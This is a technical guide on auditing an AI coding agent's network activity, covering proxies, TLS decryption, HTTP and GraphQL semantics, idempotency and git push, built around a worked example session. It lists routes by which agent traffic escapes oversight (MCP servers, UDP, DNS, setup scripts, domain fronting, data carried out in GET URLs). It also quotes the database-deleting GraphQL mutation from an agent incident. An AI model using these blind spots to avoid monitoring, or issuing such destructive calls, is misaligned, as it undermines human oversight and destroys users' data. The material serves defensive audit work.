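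MCP servers are a larger gap. These programs give an agent extra tools, such as one that posts comments on an issue tracker, through a standard interface called the Model Context Protocol. Claude Code runs local MCP servers outside the sandbox, with the user's full access. GitHub's firewall doesn't cover MCP servers or the setup steps that run before Copilot starts work. If the agent had posted the 14:02 comment through an MCP server instead of curl, neither Claude Code's proxy nor GitHub's firewall would have recorded it.

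Tools handle UDP differently. Codex's proxy accepts UDP by default through SOCKS5, a protocol for relaying more than web traffic, and its audit events have a field for the transport protocol. One version of Coder's Agent Firewall needs no special privileges, but it can't control UDP traffic, which can leave without a record. DNS lookups also bypass the proxy in INNOQ's setup and in httpjail on macOS.

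If Claude Code's sandbox can't start, for instance because a required program is missing, Claude Code by default runs commands without it, so the sandbox doesn't record them. On Windows outside the Linux subsystem, Claude Code always runs commands without the sandbox. An administrator can make Claude Code refuse to start instead.

Anthropic's solution to most of these gaps is to run all of Claude Code in a container or virtual machine, so that its web tools, local MCP servers and excluded commands are behind one boundary. The operator can then allow outbound traffic only to a proxy, as INNOQ's developer did. An MCP server hosted by another company would remain a partial exception, because it makes changes from its own machines and the operator's proxy would show only that the agent contacted it.

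## What does TLS hide, and what does it take to log the content?

A proxy that relays a CONNECT tunnel can log which host a command reached, but TLS hides what the command did there. Some proxies, such as httpjail, can read the content because they decrypt the traffic and re-encrypt it before sending it on. This takes some setup, breaks certain programs and can put passwords in the log.

### What an observer sees

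TLS encrypts the data that TCP carries, so everything the network needs to deliver packets stays visible. Someone watching the network traffic for the 14:02 comment can see both IP addresses, both port numbers, and the size and timing of each packet. They can also read the first message of the handshake, the ClientHello, in which curl lists the TLS versions and encryption methods it supports. The ClientHello normally includes the server's name in plain text, in a field called Server Name Indication (SNI), because a server that hosts several sites needs the name to choose which certificate to send.

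TLS encrypts the whole HTTP exchange: the method, path, headers, credential and body, and the status code of the reply. TLS 1.3, the current version, also encrypts most of the handshake, including the server's certificate, which TLS 1.2 sent unencrypted. It does not itself encrypt the server name, which Rescorla, Oku and colleagues (2026), in *TLS Encrypted Client Hello*, call "perhaps the most sensitive information left unencrypted".

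*Explicit QUIC Proxies for Server-Side Geo-blocking Bypass* (2026) describes a program, Stork, that must detect whether a server has accepted a request. Stork runs on the user's own machine because a proxy elsewhere in the network can't read the request or the response headers. It might be possible to infer the outcome from packet sizes and spacing, but the paper leaves that to future work.

The ClientHello also gives a clue to which program sent it, because TLS libraries list their options in different orders. In *The Security Impact of HTTPS Interception*, Durumeric, Ma and colleagues (2017) compared the major browsers with 104 other products. No two products produced the same pattern, except for eight pieces of unwanted software built on the same component. An investigator could use the pattern to tell the billing script's connection from npm's, but two programs that use the same library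 with its default settings may look identical.

### Encrypted Client Hello

Encrypted Client Hello (ECH) hides the server name too. It works like this:

1. The company that hosts the site publishes an encryption key, usually in DNS.
2. The client writes two ClientHello messages. The inner one contains the real server name. The outer one contains harmless values, including a public name that belongs to the hosting company.
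3. The client encrypts the inner message with the published key, puts it inside the outer message and sends that.
4. The hosting company's server decrypts the inner message and either completes the handshake for the real site or forwards the message to the machine that runs it.
5. If the server can't decrypt the inner message, it completes the handshake under the public name. The client doesn't send its request over that connection, but it can try again with an up-to-date key.

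The observer still learns which hosting company the client contacted. How much ECH hides therefore depends on how many sites share the company's servers, and a site with its own address gains nothing. *On the Practical Feasibility of Harvest-Now, Decrypt-Later Attacks* (2026) notes that when many sites share an address, an observer has to guess the site from packet timing and sizes, which is resource-intensive and unreliable.

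In a log, the public name looks like an ordinary server name, so a reader could conclude that the agent visited the hosting company's own website when it actually posted to a customer's. An ECH field doesn't prove that the real name was hidden, since clients that aren't using ECH may send a dummy field.

ECH does little if the observer can read the DNS lookup, so privacy-minded clients combine it with encrypted DNS. When clients use both, an operator loses the two usual ways of matching an address in a connection log to a hostname. An egress proxy that programs connect to explicitly isn't affected, because the client has to name the destination in its CONNECT request before the TLS handshake starts. Rescorla and colleagues suggest that companies disable ECH by policy on the machines they manage, or decrypt the traffic.

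The IETF published ECH as a proposed standard in March 2026, more than two years after the major browsers turned it on. That month, OpenSSL (2026) announced that its widely used encryption library would support ECH from version 4.0. Command-line tools are further behind. According to curl's *ECH*, the tool has had an experimental `--ech` option since version 8.8.0. In *HTTPS-RR and ECH*, a July 30 message to curl's developers, curl's founder Stenberg (2026) proposed ending the option's experimental status before the end of the year. He wrote that using ECH still required a copy of curl built with a particular DNS library and with either wolfSSL or a fork of OpenSSL.

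One of curl's conditions for ending the experiment is support in another widely used TLS library, and OpenSSL 4.0 seems to meet it. But for now, the curl on an agent's machine almost certainly sends the server name in plain text, as does Git over HTTPS, which uses curl's library.

### How a proxy reads the request

To decrypt traffic, a proxy needs a certificate that the client will accept as the server's. Before curl sends a request, it checks that the certificate matches the host name and is signed by a certificate authority (CA), an organisation that curl is set up to trust. No public CA should issue a certificate for `tracker.example.com` to somebody else's proxy. The operator therefore creates a private CA, consisting of a signing key and a certificate, and adds the certificate to the list that the agent's programs trust.

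Nous Research's *Egress credential-injection proxy (iron-proxy)* sets out the steps for a proxy that handles traffic from the company's Hermes agent. For the 14:02 comment they would be:

1. curl asks the proxy for a tunnel to `tracker.example.com`, and the proxy checks that the operator allows that host.
2. curl starts a TLS handshake through the tunnel. The proxy doesn't relay it. It makes a certificate for `tracker.example.com` on the spot, signs it with the private authority's key and answers as if it were the issue tracker.
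3. curl finds a valid signature from an authority it trusts, and completes the handshake.
4. The proxy opens its own TLS connection to the real tracker and checks the real certificate.
5. curl sends the POST request. The proxy decrypts it, records it, encrypts it again with the second connection's keys and forwards it. The reply comes back the same way.

There are two encrypted connections, and between them the proxy holds everything in plain text. devsandbox's *Proxy Mode*, the manual for an open-source sandbox, shows what a proxy can keep at that point. In its format, the comment might look like this (the values are invented):

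```
{"ts":"2026-12-01T14:02:11.190Z","method":"POST",
 "url":"https://tracker.example.com/issues/88/comments",
 "req_headers":{"Content-Type":["application/json"],
                "Authorization":["Bearer ..."]},
 "req_body":"eyJib2R5IjoiRml4ZWQifQ==",
 "status":201,
 "resp_headers":{"Content-Type":["application/json"]},
 "resp_body":"eyJpZCI6OTA0MX0=",
 "duration_ns":212000000,"error":""}
```

devsandbox stores the two bodies in base64, a way of writing any data as plain letters and digits, which anyone can reverse. They read `{"body":"Fixed"}` and `{"id":9041}`. With decryption turned off, the entry would contain only the host name. Termination removes only the TLS layer, however. If a script encrypts a file itself before uploading it, the proxy records a body that nobody at the operator can read.

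Termination also makes the host name more trustworthy. The client sends a host name in the CONNECT request, the ClientHello and the HTTP headers, and the three can differ. In domain fronting, a program gives the proxy the name of an allowed site, then names a different site on the same hosting service inside the encrypted request. A terminating proxy can read all three names and compare them. Anthropic recommends that users who worry about this replace Claude Code's built-in proxy with one that terminates TLS.

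A proxy may decrypt a request without logging much of it. The proxy in OpenAI's Codex has a "limited" mode that allows only GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, which are meant for reading. To enforce this over HTTPS, the proxy has to decrypt the request to check the method, but it leaves the path out of its audit events.

### Which programs have to trust the proxy

Installing the private authority's certificate in the operating system's list covers only the programs that use that list. Many bring their own.

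| Program | Where to add the certificate | Effect |
|---|---|---|
| curl | `CURL_CA_BUNDLE` | Replaces the usual list |
| Git over HTTPS | `GIT_SSL_CAINFO` | Gives Git a list to use |
| Python's `requests` library | `REQUESTS_CA_BUNDLE` | Replaces the usual list |
| Python's `ssl` module and other programs that use OpenSSL | `SSL_CERT_FILE` | Replaces the usual list |
| Node.js, including npm | `NODE_EXTRA_CA_CERTS` | Adds to the usual list |
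| Java | Java's own `cacerts` file, with the `keytool` program | Adds to the usual list |
| Go, on Linux | The system's list, or `SSL_CERT_FILE` | Adds or replaces |
| Go, on macOS | The system's list | Adds to the usual list |

The four commands in the example session would need at least four of these settings. If the operator misses one, the command that needs it stops with a certificate error before sending its request, so it changes nothing. The agent might then retry with certificate checking turned off, as curl's `-k` option does. The proxy would still record the request, but curl would no longer detect an impostor.

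The record is more likely to be complete if a setting replaces the list of trusted authorities instead of adding to it. Once curl trusts only the private authority, it rejects the real tracker's certificate, so it can't bypass the proxy even if another route to the internet is open. Node.js still trusts the public authorities, and Nous Research warns that a Node.js program could therefore connect directly where Python or curl would fail. Nous Research sets a further option to narrow this gap, but a program that supplies its own list of authorities can still bypass the proxy.

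Go programs such as `gh` and `terraform` may fail to verify certificates in Claude Code's macOS sandbox. Anthropic suggests that users who run their own decrypting proxy use the `enableWeakerNetworkIsolation` setting instead of running these programs outside the sandbox.

### What breaks

Some programs pin their certificates, which means they accept only a particular certificate or key for their own server, regardless of the trusted list, and so refuse the proxy's substitute. Examples in devsandbox's documentation include some cloud providers' software libraries and security-focused applications. However, when Durumeric and colleagues studied browsers, Chrome, Firefox and Safari skipped the pinning check if the certificate came from an authority that an administrator had installed. For a program that does its own pinning, the operator usually has to let the connection through undecrypted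 and log only a host name.

Client certificate authentication fails for a different reason. Some servers ask the client to prove its identity with a certificate and private key. The proxy is the client on the connection to the server, and it doesn't have that key. It can't forward the program's proof either, because the proof is a signature over the handshake between the program and the proxy. The operator can give the proxy the key or exempt the host from interception.

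SSH has its own encryption and doesn't use certificate authorities in this way, so a TLS proxy can relay an SSH connection, including one that carries a `git push`, but can't read it.

A proxy can forward signed requests as long as it doesn't change the signed content. AWS, for example, requires the client to compute a signature from the request's contents and a secret key, in a format called SigV4, and rejects the request if the signature doesn't match the contents.

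Claude Code has an experimental `tlsTerminate` setting, which is off by default. Anthropic added it to hide credentials from the agent's commands. A command gets a placeholder instead of the real token, and the proxy inserts the real one into requests to hosts the user has chosen. This is enough when the token is in a header, but a command that calls AWS signs its request with the placeholder, so the proxy has to detect the placeholder and sign the request again with the real key.

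The proxy can't do this for streaming uploads, presigned addresses (links that contain their own signature) or a variant format called SigV4A. By default it blocks these requests before they reach AWS. The user can have the proxy forward them, and AWS then rejects them. Nothing changes at AWS either way, but AWS could have a record of the attempt only if the proxy forwarded the request. Nous Research's proxy doesn't handle AWS signatures, so a sandbox that uses AWS has to hold the real keys.

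Re-signing also changes the request slightly, so AWS receives a different version from the one the command sent. A log made before re-signing has a placeholder where AWS's records have a real key ID, so the operator needs to know which version the log contains.

The `tlsTerminate` setting doesn't add any filtering of content, so users who want that still need a proxy of their own.

### Secrets in the log

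The `Authorization` header in the devsandbox entry contains a token that anyone who reads the log could use to post comments as the agent. Replies can also contain secrets, for instance when an API issues a new password.

devsandbox lets users write rules that look for secrets in outgoing requests, either by exact value or by pattern. A rule can block the request, redact it or just log a warning. Redaction here changes the request itself, as well as the log. If the agent's comment contained an API key, the issue tracker would publish the comment with `[REDACTED:api-key]` in the key's place. That is probably what the operator wants, but it means that the rule has altered the remote effect. With the warning option, the request goes out as it was, and devsandbox promises to keep secrets out of its log only for blocked and redacted requests. A rule also can't find what nobody described to it,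 such as a customer's name.

An operator who wants the request to arrive intact can instead redact only the stored copy. If the operator deletes the token from that copy, the log no longer shows which account made the change. The operator can avoid this by replacing the token with a keyed hash, a short code computed from the token and a secret kept elsewhere. The same token always gives the same code, so an investigator can group requests by credential, or check whether a particular token was used, without being able to read any token from the log.

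Captured bodies also take up space. devsandbox starts a new log file when the current one reaches 50 MB and keeps at most five, deleting the oldest. After a few large uploads, it could delete the record of an earlier comment, so an operator who wants to keep everything has to send the entries somewhere else.

### A key worth stealing, and weaker connections

Anyone who obtains the private authority's signing key can impersonate any website to programs that trust that authority. Nous Research calls the key "the most sensitive file" in its setup, keeps it on the host computer and gives the sandbox only the public certificate. An operator who runs a proxy on the same machine as Claude Code should check where the proxy's key is stored, because commands in Claude Code's sandbox can read most of the disk by default. Installing the certificate only inside the sandbox also helps, because someone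 who stole the key could then deceive the agent's programs but not the user's browser.

The agent's programs can't check the second connection, so its security depends on the proxy. If the proxy accepts a forged certificate, curl can't detect it, and the log records the real site's name even though an impostor responded.

Older products did this badly. Durumeric and colleagues used the products' ClientHello patterns to find intercepted connections on the web. A browser identifies itself in an HTTP header, so if the header names Firefox but the ClientHello doesn't fit Firefox, something has probably decrypted the connection on the way. They applied this test to nearly eight billion handshakes, gathered over a week at each of three services.

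| Service | Connections intercepted | Intercepted connections that became less secure |
|---|---|---|
| Firefox update servers | 4.0% | 97% |
| Popular shopping sites | 6.2% | 32% |
| Cloudflare, connections from the US | 10.9% | 54% |

These rates were more than ten times the earlier estimates and may still be too low, because the test misses any proxy that copies the browser's ClientHello. Between 10% and 40% of the intercepted connections offered encryption that attackers knew how to break. In early 2016 the researchers also tested interception products. With default settings, 11 of 12 corporate devices exposed connections to known attacks, and five had severe flaws such as failing to check certificates properly. Of 20 antivirus and similar products, 18 made connections less secure.

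The study predates TLS 1.3 and covers people's browsers, so it is weak evidence about a proxy that someone sets up for an agent today. Newer figures are scarce. *Monsters in the Middleboxes* (Fisher and Valenta, 2019) introduced a public dashboard of interception on Cloudflare's network, but in October 2026 *Explicit QUIC Proxies for Server-Side Geo-blocking Bypass* still cited the 2017 range of 4 to 10%. The proxy in that 2026 paper follows Durumeric and colleagues' recommendations, with current encryption and proper certificate checks. The old weaknesses came from careless implementation, which an operator can avoid by using a maintained proxy and keeping it up to date.

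### Reading the content without a proxy

Many TLS libraries can write each connection's encryption keys to a file, usually the one named in the environment variable `SSLKEYLOGFILE`. If the operator also records the encrypted packets, a program such as Wireshark can decrypt them later. The client still talks to the real server, so pinning, client certificates and signed requests keep working. The operator can store the keys apart from the packets and decrypt a session only if something goes wrong, which protects customers' details better than a plain-text log does.

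This method works only for programs that use the variable. If a program ignores it, nobody can decrypt its packets afterwards, because in TLS 1.3 even the server's private key normally isn't enough. The operator also has to store every packet, not just a connection log.

The other method is to read the text inside the program, as AgentSight and AgentLoupe do. This needs no private certificate authority, and it identifies the process. But a hook written for OpenSSL doesn't cover Go and Java, which have their own TLS code. The hook also captures a stream of bytes with no markers between requests. HTTP/2 mixes several requests together and compresses their headers, so the recorder has to do a fair amount of decoding to recover the method and path.

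### Combining decryption with packet capture

A terminating proxy misses traffic that isn't HTTP, while a packet capture includes it but leaves HTTPS content encrypted. Yuan and colleagues used both, running a decrypting proxy on the agent's machine, with QUIC blocked, and recording all packets alongside it. Their detector of malicious tools gave far more false alarms without decryption. To merge the two records, they kept all the packets and inserted each decrypted request and reply as an extra line. They didn't replace the encrypted packets with the matching decrypted request because matching by time is ambiguous and can delete packets that belong to something else.

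| Input to the detector | Harmless tools wrongly flagged | F1 | Balanced accuracy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Packets and decrypted requests | 2.3% | 0.998 | 0.987 |
| Packets only | 89.7% | 0.977 | 0.551 |
| Packets only, without sorting them into events | 38.5% | 0.829 | 0.669 |

F1 combines the share of malicious tools that the detector found with the share of its alarms that were correct. It barely changes between the first two rows because about 95% of the test cases were malicious, so a detector that flags nearly everything still scores well. The researchers had to cut the unsorted packets short to fit the model, so the last row's apparent improvement on the second may not be real.

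Decrypted content still has to be interpreted. Yuan and colleagues gave the merged record to two leading general-purpose models, GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5, which wrongly flagged 28.4% and 26.5% of the harmless tools, respectively. Most of these errors occurred because the models mistook ARP packets, which machines on a local network routinely send to find each other, for an intruder's scan.

### The four kinds of record compared

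| | Connection log | Host-only proxy | Terminating proxy | In-process capture |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Which host? | An address; a name if DNS or SNI supplies one | The name the client gave | The name, which the proxy can check against the certificate | The name in the request |
| Which operation? | Not shown | Not shown | Method and path of each request | Method and path, after decoding |
| What content? | Byte counts | Byte counts at most | Headers and bodies, both ways | Headers and bodies, up to the tool's size limit |
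| Which process? | Not shown | Only in some tools, such as OpenShell | Only in some tools | Yes |
| Did it succeed? | Only whether the connection opened | Only whether the tunnel opened | Status code and reply, if one arrived | Status code and reply, if one arrived |
| What does it cost? | Little storage and few secrets | Programs that can't use a proxy fail or go unrecorded | A certificate for every program, some failures, secrets in the log and a signing key to protect | Administrator rights, a hook for each TLS library and secrets in the log |

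## What did curl or a script's API call change?

The 14:02 comment is an easy case. A terminating proxy's entry for it contains the comment's text and the server's reply with the new comment's ID, which is strong evidence that the issue tracker created the comment. Many API calls leave weaker evidence, because it's unclear from the request what the client was meant to change, or from the reply what the server did.

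### Safe and idempotent methods

Under the HTTP standard, RFC 9110, a method is safe if its meaning is "essentially read-only", so that the client neither requests nor expects a change on the server. A method is idempotent if sending the same request several times is meant to have the same effect as sending it once. Deleting a file is idempotent, but posting a comment usually isn't, because sending the request twice creates two comments.

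| Method | What the client asks the server to do | Safe | Idempotent |
|---|---|---|---|
| GET | Send the resource at this address | Yes | Yes |
| HEAD | Send only the headers that GET would return | Yes | Yes |
| OPTIONS | List the ways to communicate with the resource | Yes | Yes |
| PUT | Create the resource, or replace it with this body | No | Yes |
| DELETE | Remove the resource from this address | No | Yes |
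| PATCH | Change part of the resource | No | No |
| POST | Process this body in whatever way the resource defines | No | No |

IANA's official *Hypertext Transfer Protocol (HTTP) Method Registry* (2014) lists both properties for rarer methods, such as COPY and CHECKOUT.

Both properties describe what the client requests, and the server may do more or less than that. Under the standard, a GET is still safe if clicking an ad charges the advertiser, because the person who clicked didn't ask for the charge. With a DELETE, the client asks the server to stop offering something at an address, but the server may keep the data.

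### Where the method misleads

Telegram's bot API accepts both GET and POST requests and lets programs put parameters in the URL. An agent can therefore send a message to a group chat with a GET request, which looks like a read in a log that records only hosts and methods. Logging full URLs would reveal the message, but it would also store the bot's access token, which is a working credential.

The HTTP standard forbids this kind of design. If an address ending in `page?do=delete` deletes a page, the site's owner must disable that action for safe methods such as GET, because a search engine that fetches every link would otherwise delete pages. Nottingham wrote in a 2016 draft for the IETF that many GET requests on the web have side effects anyway, though the draft included no figures.

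A GET request can also carry data out. OpenAI's example of a leaked commit message used POST, but a short message would fit in the URL of a GET. If the receiving server keeps an ordinary access log, the attacker then has a copy.

GraphQL, a query language for APIs, causes the opposite problem. A GraphQL server normally has a single address, such as `/graphql`, and the client describes the operation in the request body. According to GraphQL's *Serving over HTTP*, a server must accept POST for both reads (queries) and updates (mutations), and may accept GET only for queries. A log of methods and full addresses can therefore have identical entries for reading an account and deleting it.

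In April 2026, this kind of request deleted the production database of PocketOS, which makes software for car rental businesses. Computing's *AI coding agent goes rogue, deletes company database in nine seconds* names the agent as Cursor, running Claude Opus 4.6. The agent had found an access token on the user's machine for Railway, the company that hosted the database. Abdelwahab, in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, gives Railway's account, including the command. It was a curl POST to Railway's GraphQL address with this in the body:

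```
mutation { volumeDelete(volumeId: "3d2c42fb-...") }
```

The request body identifies the operation and the volume (a virtual disk), but it doesn't show that the volume held a production database or that deleting it would affect the backups. PocketOS's founder said the call had deleted the backups too. According to Abdelwahab, the deletion spread to the backups and made them look unavailable on Railway's website, but Railway later recovered all the data, so the website had overstated the loss.

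One request can also make several changes. A GraphQL body can contain more than one mutation, and some other APIs accept batches. If the billing API accepts batches, the script could have sent all 40 changes in one POST, and only the body would show that there were 40.

A newer HTTP method, QUERY, might eventually make GraphQL logs easier to read. *The HTTP QUERY Method* (Reschke, Snell and Bishop, 2026) defines it as a request that has a body, like POST, but is safe and idempotent. ChilliCream's *HTTP Transport* describes a GraphQL server that accepts QUERY for reads and refuses any mutation sent that way. But clients can still send reads to such a server as POST, so a POST in the log could be either a read or a mutation.

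### Allowing only GET, HEAD and OPTIONS

The cloud version of Codex has a setting that limits the agent to these three methods, in addition to its list of allowed domains. OpenAI says that it blocks all others. The setting does well against ordinary API calls and less well against the cases above:

| Request | Result |
|---|---|
| The 14:02 comment, sent as POST | Blocked |
| The billing script's 40 POST requests | Blocked |
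| Railway's `volumeDelete`, sent as POST | Blocked |
| A GraphQL read, sent as POST or QUERY | Blocked, although it changes nothing |
| A Telegram message, sent as GET | Allowed if Telegram's domain is on the list |
| A commit message in the address of a GET | Allowed if the destination's domain is on the list |

The last two rows depend entirely on the domain list. An attacker's own server wouldn't be on a short list of package registries, but Codex users can allow every domain. The agent's setup scripts are another gap because they run with full internet access before the agent starts.

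The restriction would hardly limit an agent that only needs to download things, and it would stop most accidental changes. But a log that contains only GETs doesn't prove that nothing changed.

The proxy in the local version of Codex can apply narrower rules to a particular host, matching a request's method, path, query and headers. OpenAI's example covers POST and PUT requests to GitHub's API for OpenAI's repositories. The rules can't yet match the request body, so they can't let GraphQL queries through while blocking mutations sent to the same address.

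### What the reply establishes

A 201 reply means the server has created a resource. The reply's `Location` header gives the new resource's address, or if the header is missing, the address is the one in the request. An investigator can check the resource at that address later.

A 204 means that the server did what the client asked and the response has no content. After a PUT, the response may include an ETag, an identifier for one version of a resource. The HTTP standard lets the server include one only if it saved the request body unchanged, so a 204 with an ETag is better evidence of what the server stored than a 204 without one. Even then, someone else may have changed the resource since.

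A server sends a 202 response before the requested work is done. The response body should describe the request's current status and include an address where the client can check on it. A log that keeps only status codes won't contain that address.

Some APIs report errors in the body of a 200 reply to a POST, even though a 200 should mean that the action succeeded. A GraphQL server should use a code in the 200s if its reply contains any data, even alongside errors, because HTTP has no code for partial success. The GraphQL API from Salesforce, which sells customer-management software, can return 200 even when the request names an object that doesn't exist, according to the company's *Status Codes and Error Responses*. nono's audit log records the status but not the body, so it would show such a request as an ordinary success.

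A response can also report failure when part of the request succeeded. Kraken's *Upcoming Change to GraphQL Mutation Nullability* (2026) describes a request with two mutations, in which the first succeeds and the second fails. Kraken's API used to answer with `"data": null` and a list of errors. A script that checked for data would have treated both mutations as failed and might have repeated the first. Kraken announced that from September 28 the reply would include the first mutation's result.

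Redirects are easy to misread. If a server answers a POST with 307 or 308, the client has to send the same POST to another address, and the reply to that second POST indicates whether the request succeeded. A 303 usually means that the server has processed the POST and the client should use GET to fetch a page about the result. After a 301 or 302, the standard lets the client switch from POST to GET and drop the body. If an API has moved to a new address, the log might then show a POST with a 301 followed by a GET with a 200, which looks like a success although no server acted on the body. Websites often use 302 where the standard intends 303, so after a 302 an investigator can't tell from the codes alone whether the server processed the POST.

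An error may come from the proxy rather than the remote server. When Codex's proxy blocks a request, it returns a 403 and gives the reason, such as `blocked-by-method-policy`, in the `x-proxy-error` header. Without that header, the 403 would appear to come from the remote server, which never received the request.

### The 37th billing request

Suppose that each of the billing script's requests adds a charge to one customer's account. The record of the 37th has the method, address, headers and body, then a timeout where the status code should be. At least four histories fit it:

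| What happened | Charges from this request | Charges after a plain retry that succeeds |
|---|---|---|
| The request never reached the billing server | 0 | 1 |
| The server received it but failed before adding the charge | 0 | 1 |
| The server added the charge, and the reply got lost | 1 | 2 |
| The server was still working when the script stopped waiting | 0 at first, probably 1 later | Probably 2 |

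A server that fails partway can also leave something in between, such as a charge without an invoice.

A terminating proxy helps if the reply reached it but not the script, because it would then have a status code. Otherwise the proxy's log entry has the same gap. A packet capture could show that the billing company's machine acknowledged receiving the request, which would rule out the first row but none of the others. Somebody has to check the billing company's own records to settle the matter.

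A retry could repeat a change that the first request already made. The HTTP standard advises clients not to repeat a POST automatically unless they know that repeating it is harmless or that the server never applied the first one, and it forbids proxies to do so at all. But it acknowledges that some clients guess when a retry is safe, for instance by resending a POST if an idle connection closes before any of the reply arrives. Two identical POSTs in a log may therefore be two attempts at one charge, even if the script's author wrote no retry.

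An agent might also see the timeout and run `python sync_billing.py` again. If the other 39 requests succeeded, a second run without errors would bring the total to 79 or 80 charges instead of 40.

### Idempotency keys

An idempotency key is a label that the client attaches to an operation so that the server can recognise a repeat. With Stripe, the client chooses a value of up to 255 characters and sends it in the `Idempotency-Key` header.

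Stripe's *Idempotent requests* describes how version 1 of the API, which includes most of Stripe's services, handles repeated requests. Once Stripe begins to carry out a request with a new idempotency key, it saves the status code and body of the result. When the same key arrives again, Stripe returns the saved reply if the parameters match those of the original request, and an error if they differ. It may delete a key once the key is at least 24 hours old, after which it treats a request with that key as new.

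Stripe saves nothing if it rejects the request before starting the work, for example because a parameter is invalid. The client can then fix the problem and retry.

Version 2 handles failures differently. According to Stripe's *API v2 overview*, a retry makes Stripe attempt the failed part again, and the key works for 30 days. If the billing API followed Stripe's design and the script had sent a key, a retry of the 37th request would go as follows:

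| What happened the first time | Retry with the same key, version 1 | Retry with the same key, version 2 |
|---|---|---|
| The request never arrived | Stripe adds the charge | Stripe adds the charge |
| Stripe began the work and failed | Stripe returns the saved error | Stripe tries the failed work again and returns the new result |
| Stripe added the charge, and the reply got lost | Stripe returns the saved reply | Stripe adds nothing and returns an updated reply |

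In version 1, a retry sent while the first request is still running can get a 409, which means the client should wait and try again with the same key. None of these retries produces a second charge.

The reply to a version 1 retry also helps show what happened the first time. Stripe marks a saved reply with the header `Idempotent-Replayed: true`. A successful reply with that header means the original request added the charge, and the body contains the details the script missed. A successful reply without it normally means the retry added the charge.

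But a retry can itself change the account, so it is unsuitable for someone who only wants to know what the agent did. After 24 hours, Stripe may have deleted the key, and a retry could create a second charge. Stripe then advises users to stop retrying, with either the old key or a new one, and to find out what happened by other means.

A saved error can also go out of date. After an outage, Stripe tries to repair failed operations and may create the charge after all. The saved reply doesn't change, so a client that retries can still get a 500 for a charge that now exists.

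A key prevents repeats only if the client uses the same one each time. If the billing script generates random keys at startup and doesn't save them, Stripe will treat a second run as 40 new operations. The script can avoid this by saving its keys before sending anything or by deriving each one from something stable, such as an invoice number. Rerunning it within 24 hours would then result in at most 40 charges in total.

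Idempotency keys also help the operator tell retries from separate operations in the log. Two POSTs with the same key, sent within the retention period, are attempts at one operation. If the keys differ, the server treats the POSTs as separate operations, even if their bodies are identical and the agent meant only one. To see the keys, the operator needs a log that keeps request headers, which httpjail's and OpenShell's logs don't. Stripe tells clients not to put personal data in keys, so an operator who removes the credential from a stored request can usually leave the key in.

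Stripe also lets clients put their own identifier in an object's `metadata` field when they create the object. Months later, after the key has expired, an investigator can use that identifier to trace a charge in Stripe's records to the script's request.

### Effects that never cross the proxy

When the agent posts its comment at 14:02, the issue tracker may email everyone who follows the issue. It may also send webhooks, which are HTTP requests that notify other systems of an event. A webhook could start a build or post the comment in a company's chat. The tracker's own servers send these emails and webhooks, so the agent's proxy logs only the original request and its 201 response, however many people and systems are notified.

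The billing script's requests can have similar consequences. A new charge might lead the billing service to email the customer, collect the money from a card and notify the company's accounting software. These steps may happen minutes or days after the response, and they depend on billing account settings that appear in neither the request nor the response.

If the operator's own systems receive the webhooks, those systems may have a separate record of some of these effects. The script never got a reply to its 37th request, but a webhook about a new charge could still reach the company and would be good evidence that the charge exists.

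## What did git push change?

The 14:03 command, `git push --force`, replaced the server's version of `main`. Unlike most API calls, a push request contains the old value as well as the new one, so a full capture shows which commit the branch pointed to before the push. It doesn't contain the commits that the push removed from the branch.

### The exchange

Git identifies each commit by a hash, a 40-character code computed from the commit's contents and the hashes of the commits before it. A branch is a reference, a name such as `refs/heads/main` that points to one commit. A push sends the server any objects it lacks and then changes which commit the reference points to.

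If a colleague had pushed two commits to `main` that morning and the agent had never fetched them, the agent's push would look roughly like the example below, which is based on Git's documentation of its HTTP protocol. The example uses invented, shortened hashes and omits most headers and formatting codes.

```
GET /acme/shop.git/info/refs?service=git-receive-pack

200 OK
7a41c9e...  refs/heads/main
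c93d216...  refs/heads/search-fix

POST /acme/shop.git/git-receive-pack
7a41c9e... d20b5f3... refs/heads/main
PACK (binary data)

200 OK
unpack ok
ok refs/heads/main
```

1. The client asks for the server's references and gets each name with its current hash.
2. The client sends one line for each reference it wants to change, with the old hash, the new hash and the name. A row of zeros in place of the old hash creates a reference, and zeros in place of the new one delete it.
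3. The client sends a packfile, which holds the commits and files that the server needs. Git requires one with every update, even if the server already has everything and the packfile is empty.
4. The server unpacks the data, checks that `main` still points to the old hash, runs any checks of its own and moves the reference.
5. The server reports whether the unpacking worked, then gives a result for each reference: `ok`, or `ng` with a reason.

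The line in step 2 doesn't record whether the agent used `--force`. Leon explains in *How to Scan Force Pushed Commits for Secrets* that an ordinary push goes ahead only if the server's current commit is an ancestor of the new one, and that `--force` lifts this restriction. To tell whether a captured push discarded anything, an investigator has to look up both hashes in a copy of the repository. If `d20b5f3` builds on `7a41c9e`, the push discarded nothing, even though the agent typed `--force`.

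The check in step 4 makes the old hash trustworthy. The server would have refused the update if somebody had pushed between the client's two requests, so an `ok` means that `main` pointed to `7a41c9e` just before the change. The check does little to protect the colleague's commits, though, because the client copied that hash from the server's list a moment earlier and didn't need to have fetched the commits themselves. `--force-with-lease` stops the push if the branch has moved since the last fetch, and it would have saved the colleague's work here.

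### What each record keeps

| Record | Push over HTTPS | Push over SSH |
|---|---|---|
| Connection log | Address and bytes | Address and bytes |
| Host-only proxy | Host name | Host name, if SSH goes through the proxy |
| Terminating proxy that logs web addresses | Repository, and that the command was a push | Host name at most |
| Terminating proxy that also logs bodies | Branch, both hashes, new commits and result | Host name at most |
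| Git's output on the agent's machine | Branch, shortened hashes and result | The same |

A push and a fetch both use POST, but with different paths. A push goes to `git-receive-pack` and a fetch to `git-upload-pack`, which are named for what the server does. httpjail's log would therefore show that the agent pushed to this repository, but not to which branch. Codex's audit events omit the path, so they wouldn't show even that. A proxy that allows only GET, HEAD and OPTIONS would block this kind of fetch along with the push.

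As with GraphQL, a 200 reply doesn't prove that the change happened, because the server reports a refusal in the response body. A push can also partly succeed, as in an example in Git's documentation where the server accepts a change to `debug` but refuses one to `master`.

The hashes come before the packfile, so a recorder that keeps only the first part of a large request will probably still have them. Reading the packfile takes more work. Git may store a file in it as differences from one the server already has, and the investigator then needs a copy of the repository to reconstruct the file.

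Over SSH, the client logs in to the server and runs `git-receive-pack` there, with the repository's path as an argument. The same exchange then takes place inside the encrypted session, where a TLS-terminating proxy can't read it. Git's own output can fill in some of what is missing. An older version of GitHub's *Removing sensitive data from a repository* includes this line from a forced push:

```
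+ 48dc599...051452f main -> main (forced update)
```

Seven characters of each hash are usually enough to find the commit. The agent's transcript should contain this line unless the command used `--quiet`. The hosting service's records are better evidence because the agent controls the command.

### GitHub's own records

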